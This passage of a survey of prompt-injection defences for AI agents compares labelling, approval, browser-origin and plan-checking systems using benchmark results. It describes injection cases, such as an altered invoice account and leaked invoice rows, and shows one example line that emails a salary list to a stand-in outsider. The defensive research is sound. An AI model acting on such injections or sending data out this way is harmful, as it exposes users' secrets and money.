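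Prudentia has no matching option to declassify a whole document. Whether it is appropriate to share private information depends on the situation, so Prudentia leaves that decision to approvals of individual calls.

The code that enforces the policies is the same as in FIDES. If the planner plans badly, the user gets extra questions or the task fails, but no call bypasses the policy.

### Fewer questions on AgentDojo

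The comparison covers four agents. The basic agent asks a person to approve every consequential call. The second adds labels and asks only when a call fails its policy. FIDES adds hidden variables, and Prudentia adds the planning described above. The figures are averages over five runs without attacks and assume that a person approves whatever a successful run needs.

| Agent | o3-mini: interventions | o3-mini: completed with none | o3-mini: completed with any number | o4-mini: interventions | o4-mini: completed with none | o4-mini: completed with any number |
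|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 48.2 | 24.3% | 62.5% | 48.6 | 32.8% | 70.1% |
| Basic with labels | 32.4 | 35.5% | 62.5% | 34.6 | 42.5% | 70.1% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% | 64.3% | 36.8 | 53.2% | 75.7% |
| Prudentia | 16.4 | 59.1% | 69.8% | 19.2 | 59.4% | 73.2% |

With o3-mini, the labels alone removed a third of the interventions without changing what the agent did. Prudentia needed slightly fewer interventions than FIDES, a difference within the variation between runs, but it completed 9 percentage points more tasks on its own. It needed about one intervention for every four tasks it completed, compared with four for every five with the basic agent.

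With o4-mini and no limit on interventions, FIDES completed slightly more tasks than Prudentia but needed nearly twice as many interventions. The difference in completed tasks is small enough to be due to chance.

Prudentia's benefit depends heavily on the model. With GPT-5, it completed 72.7% of tasks alone, compared with 57.1% for FIDES, and needed 7.3 interventions instead of 41.3. With GPT-4o, an older model that doesn't reason before answering, Prudentia did worse than FIDES, completing 42.5% of tasks alone instead of 50.3% and needing 23.8 interventions instead of 7.8. It also cost about twice as much as FIDES with that model, at roughly four to six cents per task.

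When the user is asked fewer questions, they also have fewer chances to catch ordinary mistakes. If the planner model misreads the amount in the user's request, all the data is still labelled trusted, so the wrong amount is paid. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that labels can replace approvals only as a defence against attacks.

### Whether people approve the right calls

No people took part in these experiments. The claim that no attack succeeds assumes that a person would review every blocked call and stop the malicious ones. Studies of real approvals make that assumption doubtful.

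One reason is approval fatigue, which Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes as people no longer paying close attention to what they approve. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a study in which a research vendor had 1,053 paid testers use Claude Code, the company's coding agent, and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

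The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than usual. The company also used the result to argue for replacing most prompts with a model that screens commands. Still, the fall from 17% to 5% is consistent with fatigue.

In normal use, people approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans it presents. They may reject a plan only because they would do the work differently, but they seem to read it. This is mildly encouraging for endorsement, which also replaces many small questions with one larger one. However, nobody has tested Prudentia's endorsement requests on users.

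Asking less often doesn't necessarily make people more careful. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people without a software background supervise a simulated assistant that proposed 18 actions. Seven went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading bank transactions or buying a lounge pass. Participants who had to decide on every action approved 40.3% of the excessive ones, or 32% excluding the most harmless, a phone call to the airport.

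Another group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money. This reduced the average number of questions from 18.0 to 10.9, but the group let more excessive actions through. They chose "ask" for 81% of their rules and then approved 67% of the excessive actions they were asked about. Yan added some participants to this group without random assignment, so the comparison is less reliable than a fully randomised one.

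Many prompts also leave out what the user needs to know. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of problems with agents and files. In 80 of them, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31, the prompts were uninformative. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the prompt doesn't show what the script does.

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much improving the prompts helps. In one of their examples, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. An injection leads the agent to copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, recipient and file name all look fine, so only someone who knows what went into the file can see the problem.

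The 80 participants each judged six safe and six unsafe requests, using one of four kinds of prompt:

| The prompt contains | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23 s |
| Also the user's restrictions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 39 s |
| The same facts, arranged to show where the data came from and what the call would do | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33 s |

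More information clearly helped. The further improvement from arranging it could be due to chance. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests. They also had more reason for suspicion than real users have, because half of all the requests were unsafe.

Labels can supply some of this information. Microsoft suggests prompts that show where untrusted data came from or who would gain access to private data. Its sample policy for messages in Teams, the company's chat program, shows who would gain access, but lists them by user ID, which few people would recognise.

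Code determines when Prudentia prompts the user, so an attacker can't prevent the prompt but may still influence its text. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of prompts that resist this influence to future work. People are generally poor at noticing such manipulation. In *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026), only 8.6% of 303 participants noticed when a compromised agent misled them.

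### Routes past a refusal in APPA

If people are unreliable approvers, it helps to have ways past a refusal that don't need human approval. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) presents a system built around this idea, the Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra. Like FIDES, it labels the conversation and checks each call.

If a call fails because the context is untrusted or too secret, the agent can't fix this by reading more, since that never loosens the label. APPA's refusals come with a list of steps that would help. Depending on what the developer has set up, the list can include:

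- Completing a required step first, such as logging a legal clearance before sending contract terms to a client.
- Getting a ruling on this one call from an authority, which may be a person, a fixed rule or another model.
- Using a cleaned version of the data, for instance after trusted code has removed personal details.
- Reading the data in a separate branch of the conversation.
- Accepting that the label will become more restrictive and giving up some later calls.

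To build the list, APPA searches the possible combinations of steps the developer has registered. The search always finishes, and it finds a route if those steps allow one. It can't find a route that needs an unregistered step, such as asking a colleague to change a file's access settings.

In one of the team's test tasks, the agent has to confirm that Alice Chen's personnel record is on file and then send a routine update to the whole company. Once the agent has read the record, its context is too secret for a company-wide email, even though the email contains nothing from the record. A branch avoids this:

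```
main conversation:   label = everyone in the company may read
  branch:            starts as a copy, with the same label
                     reads Alice's record      -> label = HR only
                     returns on_file = true
main conversation:   receives "true", label unchanged
                     sends the company-wide update
```

Before the branch starts, the agent fixes the form of the answer, such as a yes or no, a number within limits or a choice from a list. Free text isn't allowed. This resembles the typed answers in FIDES, but a branch can also call tools, under the same checks. Discarding the branch doesn't undo those calls, such as sending an email.

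As in FIDES, an injection could still make the answer false. Checking the answer's form also doesn't make the answer public. The main conversation's label stays unchanged only if the developer has declared that everyone in the company may receive this kind of answer.

A ruling is narrower than an endorsement in Prudentia. It covers one exact call and changes no labels, so the next call that fails needs its own ruling. The developer also limits what each authority may approve. If the authority is a person, a long task can again produce enough questions to cause approval fatigue, a problem Kravchenko and colleagues leave to future work.

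### Combined tools and missing labels

APPA checks each call twice. Some tools both read and send, such as one that fetches a confidential ledger and emails it to outside lawyers. If the code looked only at the context's label before the call, the email would pass, because the agent hasn't read anything secret yet. APPA therefore checks the label the context would have afterwards:

$$\ell_{\text{after}} = \ell_{\text{context}} \sqcup \ell_{\text{expected result}}$$

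The expected label comes from the developer's description of the tool. In case that description was wrong, the second check examines the actual result before it reaches the model. This check can keep the data out of the conversation, but it can't undo what the tool has already done, such as sending an email.

Few tools come with labels. Microsoft's Agent Framework treats unlabelled tools as trusted by default. APPA instead marks the missing part of a label as unknown and lets the agent continue until a check depends on that part. It then runs a function that the developer has registered to work out the label, with a limit on how permissive the result can be. If no function is registered, or the function fails, APPA blocks the call.

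A developer can therefore start with a few labelled tools and add more later. This is as safe as labelling everything in advance only if these functions never assign an overly permissive label.

### What the APPA tests found

Kravchenko and colleagues used two benchmarks. AgentThreatBench is an existing set of 24 tasks involving poisoned memory, hijacked agents and data theft. Bench-Corp, which they designed, has 20 office tasks such as the one about Alice's record. They ran both benchmarks with three models, using ordinary instructions and instructions that encouraged the agent to obey text in its data. The table shows the range of results across models and instructions.

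| Defence | Bench-Corp: tasks completed | Bench-Corp: attacks succeeded | AgentThreatBench: tasks completed | AgentThreatBench: attacks succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No enforcement | 88–93% | 30–38% | 83–98% | 12–67% |
| APPA | 87–91% | 0% | 64–77% | 0% |
| FIDES, two configurations | 36–46% | 26–35% | 24–74% | 0–31% |

No attack succeeded in 1,320 runs with APPA. APPA barely reduced the number of completed tasks on Bench-Corp, but the team designed that benchmark to exercise APPA's features. The reduction on AgentThreatBench is probably a better guide to the reduction elsewhere, although some of it comes from a scorer that rejects correct answers that don't contain an exact phrase.

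The comparison with FIDES is weak evidence about FIDES itself. Kravchenko and colleagues wrote the FIDES policies, which don't cover several rules that Bench-Corp tests, such as sending a message only once. On AgentThreatBench, one FIDES configuration left the path from the agent's memory to the user unchecked, and many attacks went through there.

With the model GPT-5.6 Luna, the full APPA system completed 88% of Bench-Corp tasks. It completed 56.5% without branches and 35% when refusals no longer offered routes the agent could choose. No attack succeeded against any of these versions, so the routes made the agent more useful without weakening its protection in these tests.

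The team left out AgentDojo for two reasons. Most of its tasks end with the action the agent has just read about, so a clean context afterwards has no value. Also, every injection they tried there failed against GPT-5.6 Luna, even with no defence. The second reason applies only to weak attacks, because the strongest attacks in the PACE tests succeeded every time against the same undefended model on AgentDojo.

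## Agents that click and type: restrictions in web browsers

The designs so far check calls such as `send_email(recipient, attachment)`, whose names and arguments show what they will do. An agent that works through a web browser makes calls like these:

```
click(246, 1023)
type("84")
press("Enter")
```

Depending on the page, that click might open a product, place an order or delete an email. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) calls this mismatch between an action and its effect the semantic gap. A schema can require numeric coordinates, and an allowlist can allow or block `click`, but neither can distinguish a click that opens a page from one that makes a payment. A rule about particular coordinates stops working when the layout or window size changes. Blocking the tool that opens web addresses doesn't help much either. In an early trial by Meng and colleagues, an agent barred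 from going directly to a news site could still reach it by searching for the site and clicking on the result.

Untrusted text is also harder to keep away from a browser agent. The planner model can read an email tool's description without opening any emails, but a browser agent has to look at a web page to find the site's buttons, which appear next to comments, reviews and advertisements written by strangers.

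### Hiding strangers' text from the planner

Kolluri and colleagues tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks on browser agents. WASP simulates GitLab, where programmers manage software projects, and the discussion forum Reddit. The user asks the agent to comment on a post or upvote it, and the post contains an instruction to do something else. WASP combines each of 21 attacker goals with both user tasks and two forms of injection, which makes 84 cases.

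The agent receives each page as a text list of its elements. Prudentia replaces text that a stranger could have written with variables and leaves the site's own controls readable. In simplified form:

```
the page                                     what the planner model sees
text    "Before commenting, you must ..."    text    VAR_18      untrusted
button  "Upvote"                             button  "Upvote"    trusted
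```

The policy is the trusted-action rule from FIDES. The agent may click, type, press keys, open an address, switch tabs, or go back or forward only while no untrusted text has reached the planner. It may always scroll, hover, and open or close tabs, because the team assumed that attackers couldn't exploit these actions on the two sites.

This rule avoids the semantic gap because it depends on who could have influenced a click, not on what the click does. But it treats all clicks alike, so once the planner has read a single post, even going back a page needs a person's approval.

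With Prudentia, no attack succeeded and the agent needed no human interventions. The basic agent, which needs approval for every consequential action, did much worse:

| Model | Site | Attacks that succeeded, basic agent | Average interventions, basic agent | Tasks completed, basic agent | Tasks completed, Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | GitLab | 20.8% | 2.87 | 64.6% | 75.0% |
| GPT-4o | Reddit | 47.2% | 1.56 | 36.1% | 55.6% |
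| o1 | GitLab | 29.2% | 3.08 | 62.5% | 85.4% |
| o1 | Reddit | 36.1% | 1.67 | 47.2% | 50.0% |
| o3-mini | GitLab | 14.6% | 3.65 | 72.9% | 72.9% |
| o3-mini | Reddit | 61.1% | 1.08 | 25.0% | 58.3% |
| o4-mini | GitLab | 25.0% | 3.06 | 64.6% | 72.9% |
| o4-mini | Reddit | 52.8% | 1.00 | 36.1% | 63.9% |

An attack counts as successful here if it diverted the agent from the user's task, even if the attacker never achieved their goal. Prudentia completed more tasks in seven of the eight rows, probably because the injected text no longer interfered with the planner.

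The tasks were unusually favourable to this design because neither requires reading the post. The planner already has the page to visit and the action to take there, and the "Upvote" button is trusted, so it never has to open a variable. The test shows that masking works when an agent can ignore what strangers have written, but not how Prudentia would handle a request to find the comment that reports a crash and reply to it.

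In *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) extend masking to such tasks. Their planner receives a placeholder such as "review" and can query a quarantined model about the hidden text. As with typed answers in FIDES, the reply must be yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list. On 100 tasks across ten websites that the team built, agents completed about as many tasks with masking as without it, at 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost. Half of the tasks required untrusted text.

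On a real copy of GitLab, the agents could no longer complete some tasks that needed free text, such as saying what feature an issue requests. They could complete these tasks again when a user could approve the text before it reached the planner. As in FIDES, typed answers can still be false, which could lead the agent to act on the wrong issue or project.

Someone also has to mark the untrusted parts of each page. Nikolić and colleagues did this by hand for GitLab, Reddit and Booking.com, and needed only 15 to 30 rules per site. They also had a language model write the rules from the structure of the pages, with all the text removed so that an injection couldn't influence it. The model missed no kinds of untrusted element on Reddit, about 7% on Booking.com and about 10% on GitLab. Any miss would expose the planner directly to an attacker's text.

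### Limiting the sites an agent can use

Browsers already use the same-origin policy to stop a script on one site from reading data from another. An origin is the combination of protocol, host name and port in a web address, so a bank and a forum have different origins. An agent can defeat this separation by reading a page on one site and typing what it read into another.

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Google's approach, Agent Origin Sets. For each task, the browser keeps one set of origins that the agent may only read and another where it may also click and type. If the user wants a recipe's ingredients added to a shopping basket, the recipe site could be in the read-only set and the shop in the other. The user's bank would be in neither, so a prompt injection in the recipe couldn't make the agent open the user's account. The browser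 also hides embedded frames, such as advertisements, from the agent if they come from origins outside both sets.

These sets are built during the task. The planner proposes sites as it works, and a separate gating function decides whether each is relevant to the task. For new sites, this function is a variant of a model that Google built to compare the agent's actions with the user's goal. It doesn't see the content of web pages, so an attacker can't give it instructions directly through a page. Code then restricts the agent to the sites that the model judged relevant.

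An origin also covers many different actions. If the agent may comment on a GitLab issue, an injection in that issue could still make it delete a GitLab project, since both actions take place on the same origin. Data can also pass from any site the agent may read to any site where it may write.

Little public evidence exists on how well the sets work. Parker reports no attack rates, and says that Chrome's first version tracks only the set of sites where the agent can both read and write. Roesner and Kohlbrenner, in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers with built-in agents in early 2026. They demonstrated a complete cross-site data theft only in ChatGPT Atlas, but found that Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome, and Perplexity's Comet also met the preconditions for this attack, so the separation between sites depended on the model resisting injections.

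*Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) addresses the same problem with SOPGuard, a system that labels data with the origin it came from and carries the label over to whatever the agent writes. Before the agent enters text on a page, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with the page's origin and requires the user to confirm if they differ. This reduced violations on the team's benchmark to zero and slowed the browser by 2% to 6%.

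Wang and colleagues found that data can cross between sites even without an attacker. For example, an agent may summarise a page that contains a frame from another site and then type the summary into the outer page. SOPGuard would catch this, but it would also interrupt the recipe task, where the user wants the agent to copy between sites.

### Checking requests instead of clicks

However an agent gets to the checkout page, the browser has to send the shop's server a message to place the order. These messages, called HTTP requests, usually have a fixed meaning:

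```
POST gitlab.com/-/user_settings/ssh_keys         add a login key to the account
POST amazon.com/checkout/p/*/spc/place-order*    place an order
```

ceLLMate is a Chrome extension that checks these requests. It needs a list of the site's security-relevant requests and their meanings, which Meng and colleagues call an agent sitemap and expect the site's developers to publish. The developers, or another trusted party such as a company's administrator, also write a set of policies. One might allow purchases up to a given amount.

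For each task, a language model selects the policies the agent needs and fills in values such as the amount. The user confirms the selection before the agent starts. The model receives only the user's request and the policy descriptions, so a web page can't influence it. Three models selected exactly the right policies for at least 94% of tasks in each of the shopping, travel and software project categories. Some of the mistakes gave the agent more rights than it needed.

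Even a simple spending limit takes some care to enforce. Amazon's order request doesn't include the total, so ceLLMate has to read it from the checkout page. It also slows the agent down after a change to the basket, to avoid checking an old total. As with Progent's payment rules, the limit applies to each order separately unless ceLLMate counts the orders too.

To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues wrote 12 scripts that carried out WASP's attacker goals on GitLab directly, as if an injection had taken complete control of the agent. The active policies allowed only reading and writing issues, and ceLLMate blocked all 12 scripts. This is good evidence that the enforcement code works, but the test didn't cover attacks that use only permitted actions, because every script needed a prohibited one. The team left out WASP's Reddit cases, where most of the goals involve posting harmful comments,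 and a policy that allows comments can't filter them by content.

The ceLLMate team didn't measure how many ordinary tasks an agent completes with it running. In a test on GitLab, pages took 7% to 15% longer to load. Coverage is a bigger concern, because if a sitemap is incomplete or wrong, the affected requests get only the browser's existing protection. The team's own GitLab sitemap lists 51 operations. ceLLMate also can't interpret WebSocket messages, which many sites use for live updates.

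*AC4A* (2026) enforces permissions on the page itself. A configuration file lists the permission that each element requires. Before the agent sees the page, the software covers the elements that the agent may not use. In a demonstration with a game's website, an agent with only read permission saw the list of past games with a dark box over each delete button.

### Writing the plan before seeing the screen

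CaMeL's planner writes its whole program before reading any data, which seems impossible for an agent that needs to see the screen to know where to click. Foerster and colleagues made it work by having the planner prepare for many possible screens. A quarantined model looks at the screen while the program runs, and its answers determine which branch to take and where to click:

```
screen = describe_screen()
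if not check(screen, "the settings page is open"):
    click(find("the settings button"))
click(find("the font size box"))
```

These programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, about four times as many lines and ten times as many branches as CaMeL's AgentDojo programs. About half of each program was fallback code that went unused in a given run.

The team tested the design on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in desktop programs and a browser. For each agent, the table shows how many of the tasks solved without the defence could still be solved with it.

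| Model operating the computer | Tasks solved without the defence | Still solved in one attempt | Still solved at least once in five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (42%) | 39 (65%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (29%) | 48 (63%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28%) | 62 (57%) |

The paper's headline figure, that frontier models retain up to 57% of their performance, comes from the last column. It applies in practice only if something can pick out the successful attempt and the failed ones do no damage. In a single attempt, each agent lost more than half of these tasks. The 19% improvement the paper reports for small models counts the best of three attempts. Results depended mainly on the planner model, so newer planners may do better.

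A fixed program prevents an attacker from adding steps, but each click still goes to the coordinates that the quarantined model returns. Misleading content on the screen can make that model return the wrong coordinates or send the program down the wrong branch. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. They left out CaMeL's policies, which could otherwise limit the damage, because a policy can't evaluate a pair of coordinates. They tried checking the model's answers against the page's code and against a second model, but some attacks still succeeded, and broader checks interfered with legitimate tasks.

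Piet, Chow and colleagues therefore propose replacing clicks with named functions that have typed arguments and documented effects (*Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm*, 2026). They examined the tasks in WebArena, a benchmark that uses working copies of websites. They judged that an ordinary program could do 81% of the tasks and that the rest needed a model only to interpret text. Their estimate assumes that every site has a complete and trustworthy set of functions, which few sites have.

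The same group at Berkeley then built such an agent, Baya, which Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026) present in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*. Its planner works with functions like this one:

```
search_products(query: str) -> List[ProductListing]
```

The planner writes a program and tests it against simulated responses, with no access to the live site. If the program fails on the real site, the planner receives a restricted error message and can revise the program up to three times. This is safe only if the error messages never include text written by the site's users, and the people who write the functions have to ensure that.

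Across three models, Baya completed an average of 77.8% of 581 WebArena tasks. An agent that had the same functions and a browser, but chose each step as it went, completed 66.7%, and one with only a browser completed 55.1%. Baya's lead over the agent with the same functions shrank to 2.4 percentage points with GPT-5.6 Luna. On WASP, no attack diverted Baya, while attacks diverted the other two agents in 16.2% and 25.5% of cases. Baya took about five and a half minutes and cost $0.70 per task, compared with a minute and a half and $0.34 for the agent with the same functions.

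These figures don't include the work of preparing each site. Chow and colleagues assembled the functions for WebArena's sites by hand. The forum's own programming interface had only 16 operations, enough for a third of its tasks, so the team wrote browser scripts for the missing ones. An agent could explore new sites and write such functions automatically, but an injection it encountered there could influence code that the planner would later trust. Baya also isn't designed to stop an attacker from affecting the outcome of a permitted action, so a dishonest seller's text could still lead it to buy a counterfeit.

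## Small planning languages checked before they run: SPA and Guardians

CaMeL checks each tool call while its program runs, so it may block the fourth call after the first three have taken effect. Some newer designs check the whole plan before its first step. To make this practical, they have the planner model write in a language much smaller than Python, because ordinary code can determine more about a plan in advance when the language is less expressive.

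### What a checker can and can't decide

Suppose a checker has to determine whether this program ever emails the salary list:

```
search_for_a_proof()                          may run forever
send_email("eve@example.net", salary_list)
```

The email goes out only if the search ends. A checker that always answered such questions correctly could also tell whether any program eventually stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that this question is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can answer it correctly for every program. In 1953 Henry Rice extended the result to every question about what programs do, except those with the same answer for all programs.

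A checker for a general-purpose language can still be useful if it rejects whatever it can't prove safe. But the more freedom the language allows, the more harmless programs the checker will reject. A few restrictions make checking much easier. If loops can only go through a finite list, every plan ends, provided its tools do. If plans can't define functions or compute the names of tools, every possible call is visible in the text. The checker can then read the plan once from top to bottom, treating both branches of each condition as possible.

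The check is still slightly conservative, because it rejects a forbidden call even in a branch that could never run. But it always either accepts or rejects the plan before any of it runs.

### SPA's six kinds of step

Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, present a language of this kind, published in August 2026. A plan is a list of steps in JSON, and there are six kinds:

| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
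| `retrieve` | loads a result saved during an earlier request |
| `tool` | calls a tool |
| `q-llm` | has a quarantined model turn text into a structured answer |
| `display` | shows something to the user |
| `condition` | runs one of two lists of steps |
| `loop` | runs a list of steps for each item in a collection |

Only `tool` steps can change anything in the outside world. Their arguments can be fixed values, variables, fields of variables, or lists and objects built from these. Arithmetic, text templates and functions are not available. A condition makes a single comparison, such as whether two values are equal or whether a list contains an item. The planner expresses "and" by nesting conditions.

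The planner model writes the whole plan in one attempt. If the plan is malformed or unsafe, SPA ends the request with a failure and sends the planner no explanation. This prevents error messages from carrying an attacker's text to the planner and stops the planner from adjusting an unsafe plan until it passes.

### Bob's request as a SPA plan

For Bob's request, where the meeting notes contain the address and the document's name, the plan could look like this. It omits the answer's exact format and the two short descriptions that every `tool` and `q-llm` step must include.

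```
{"steps": [
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "find_recent_notes",
   "inputs": {}, "output": "notes"},

  {"type": "q-llm", "inputs": {"var": "notes"},
   "prompt": "Find Bob's address and the document he asked for.",
   "output": "details"},

  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "fetch_document",
   "inputs": {"title": {"attr": {"var": "details", "path": ["title"]}}},
   "output": "report"},

  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "send_email",
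   "inputs": {"recipient":  {"attr": {"var": "details", "path": ["address"]}},
              "attachment": {"var": "report"}},
   "output": "receipt"}
]}
```

Before running it, SPA works out a label for every variable. Whoever deploys the system sets two limits for each tool $f$: the most secret data it may receive, $C_{\text{in}}(f)$, and the least trusted data it accepts, $I_{\text{in}}(f)$. For a step with arguments $x_1, \dots, x_n$, SPA combines their labels with the label $pc$ of the decisions that led to the step:

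$$\lambda = pc \sqcup \lambda(x_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \lambda(x_n)$$

The step passes if

$$C(\lambda) \le C_{\text{in}}(f) \quad\text{and}\quad I(\lambda) \ge I_{\text{in}}(f)$$

Suppose `send_email` accepts secret data but not untrusted data, while the other two tools accept anything. The notes are secret and untrusted. As in FIDES, the quarantined model's answer inherits that label, and so does the report. The last step therefore fails the check, and SPA rejects the whole plan without opening the notes.

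SPA runs the check before the address is known, so it returns the same result whether the notes contain Bob's address or Eve's. The result changes only if the user supplies more of the details. The table assumes that the document store itself is secret and trusted.

| The user's request contains | Recipient | Attachment | Plan |
|---|---|---|---|
| neither the address nor the title | untrusted | untrusted | rejected |
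| Bob's address | trusted | untrusted | rejected |
| Bob's address and the title | trusted | trusted | accepted |

FIDES would send the email in the first row because Bob is already allowed to read the report. SPA can't make that exception, since its limits are set for each tool and don't depend on the recipient. These limits also apply to all of a tool's arguments together, so an untrusted attachment blocks an email even when the user typed the address. SPA has no endorsement, so the user can't approve a rejected plan.

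SPA also checks whether the decision to take an action depends on untrusted data. A user might ask the agent to email the agenda to bob@example.org if the notes say he is coming. The address and the agenda are trusted, but the decision to send depends on the untrusted notes, so $pc$ is untrusted inside the branch and SPA rejects the plan.

### Results that keep their labels

SPA saves the results of each request for use in later requests. It stores each result's value, label and description separately, and shows the planner model only the description. The planner wrote most of that description when it made the earlier plan, before any tool had run, so the description contains no text from an attacker.

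In an example from Girrens and Wang, a user asks on Monday for an invoice from a company called Acme, and an attacker has altered the payment account on it. On Tuesday the user says to pay the invoice they discussed the day before. The planner can see that a saved invoice exists and which fields it has, but not their contents. It writes a `retrieve` step, which brings back the invoice with the label it had on Monday. The account number is still untrusted, so SPA rejects a payment that uses it, as it would even if the invoice were genuine.

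### How many tasks survive the check

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with GPT-5.4-nano, a small model. They also divided each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five successive requests, so that later requests needed earlier results. In half of the setups, SPA hid the installed tools' descriptions from the planner, in case one contained an injection. The planner instead used tool descriptions that a model had invented from the user's request, and SPA tried to match these to real tools afterwards.

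| Setup | Single request: tasks completed | Single request: attacks succeeded | Several requests: tasks completed | Several requests: attacks succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Label checks off | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Label checks on | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |
| Tools hidden, checks off | 14.1% | 0.0% | 12.6% | 0.0% |
| Tools hidden, checks on | 6.7% | 0.0% | 9.7% | 0.0% |

The completion rates are for runs without attacks. With the label checks off, planning first was enough to stop all but 4 of 949 attacks. Those four were all on a single banking task; three transferred money and one changed the user's password. The label checks stopped all four but reduced the completion rate by 24 percentage points. As with CaMeL's policies, AgentDojo probably understates the checks' value. The 0.2% in the second row is two runs, and SPA had rejected the plan in both, so the scorer probably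 counted them by mistake.

The agent completed very few tasks when the tools were hidden from it. In about three quarters of those runs, SPA couldn't match a tool the agent had invented to a real one. Even the low completion rates overstate how well the agent did, because the scorer counts five of the banking tasks as complete when the agent has done nothing.

When an earlier request had stored what a later one needed, the planner retrieved it 95.4% of the time with the checks off and 89.9% with them on. In a further test with the checks off, the planner could also read the saved values, and attacks still succeeded only 0.6% of the time. This is little evidence about delayed attacks, because the injections weren't designed to lie dormant until a later request.

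### Guardians: a solver checks the plan

Labels can show that a plan never sends a secret to the wrong tool, but not that it deletes only the files the user named. Erik Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* (2025, reprinted in *Communications of the ACM* in January 2026) proposes checking such conditions with an automated solver. As in SPA, the model writes a complete workflow in JSON before any tool runs. Software then tries to prove that the workflow meets a specification, and runs it only if the proof succeeds. Meijer compares this to Java, which verifies a compiled program before executing it.

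In one of his examples, the user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The model takes a shortcut and writes a plan with one call, `delete_file("*.txt")`, which deletes every text file. Let $S$ be the set of files before the plan runs and $S'$ the set afterwards. An obvious specification for the task is

$$\textit{Task}:\quad \texttt{foo.txt} \notin S' \;\wedge\; \texttt{bar.txt} \notin S'$$

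The tool's description guarantees that no file matching the pattern remains:

$$\textit{Tool}:\quad \forall f:\; f \text{ matches } \texttt{*.txt} \Rightarrow f \notin S'$$

The solver looks for a counterexample, a pair $S, S'$ for which *Tool* is true and *Task* is false. It finds none, because if no text file remains, neither of the two named files remains. The plan passes even though it would also delete `notes.txt`.

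The specification says what must change but not what must stay the same. Computer scientists call the missing part a frame condition, and here both sides need one. The task needs a condition that every file other than the two named ones stays as it was. The tool needs a condition that files not matching the pattern stay as they were. (Meijer writes out only the tool's.) Now the solver finds a counterexample:

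```
S  = {foo.txt, bar.txt, notes.txt}
S' = {}

Tool:  true     no text file remains, and there were no other files to keep
Task:  false    notes.txt should still be there
```

The plan fails the check. A plan that deletes the two files by name passes, but only because of the tool's frame condition. Without it, the solver would have to allow that deleting `foo.txt` might also remove `notes.txt`.

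The proof therefore guarantees only what the specification states, and somebody has to write that specification. In the conference talk *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer (2026) suggests translating the user's request into a specification automatically, alongside business rules the company has formalized. If a language model does the translating and omits the frame condition, the solver will approve the plan that deletes everything. The system still depends on the model to state what the user wants, even though it no longer trusts the model to act.

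Solvers are also subject to the undecidability results of Turing and Rice, so they can't settle every statement about all files or all customers, and they sometimes stop without an answer. Meijer's rule for agents is "guilty until proven safe", so an unproved plan doesn't run and the model writes another. SPA doesn't allow a second attempt. Retrying does no harm if the specification is complete, but if it has a gap, each new plan is another chance for an unsafe one to pass the check.

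Some conditions can be checked only when the plan runs. Meijer describes a policy that keeps the contents of emails from reaching anyone outside the company. For Bob's request, the solver can't determine in advance whether the address in the notes will be inside the company. Meijer accepts such runtime checks and points out that Java also checks some things only while a program runs.

The article reports no experiments, and Meijer acknowledges that nobody had formally measured how writing whole plans affects an agent's performance. There is an open-source implementation, also called Guardians. According to *Background And Related Work*, from the documentation of a similar project called clauz3, Guardians tracks data from sources to forbidden destinations, checks the order of tool calls, and uses the solver Z3 for conditions like the ones above.

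The two projects differ on Python. In his talk, Meijer rejects it because importing a Python module runs code, which can change what later operations do. In clauz3, the agent writes ordinary Python together with a contract, such as "emails only Bob, at most once", and Z3 checks the program against the contract before the user approves it. The contracts have to stay simple enough for Z3 to check. According to clauz3's *Guardians Synergies*, they can't yet express where a value came from or which action must come before another.

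### ETAS: the order of actions as part of a type

The order of actions is the main concern of Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, a language from a group in Hong Kong. Developers use it to write the whole application around a model, including its agents and tools, and a compiler checks the result. The type of each function lists the effects it may have. In ETAS's notation, a function that asks a person before emailing a report might read:

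```
spec AskFirst = Approval.request >> Mail.send;

flow send_report(r: Report) -> unit
     ![Approval.request, Mail.send] ~ AskFirst {
  if perform Approval.request(r) { perform Mail.send(r); }
}
```

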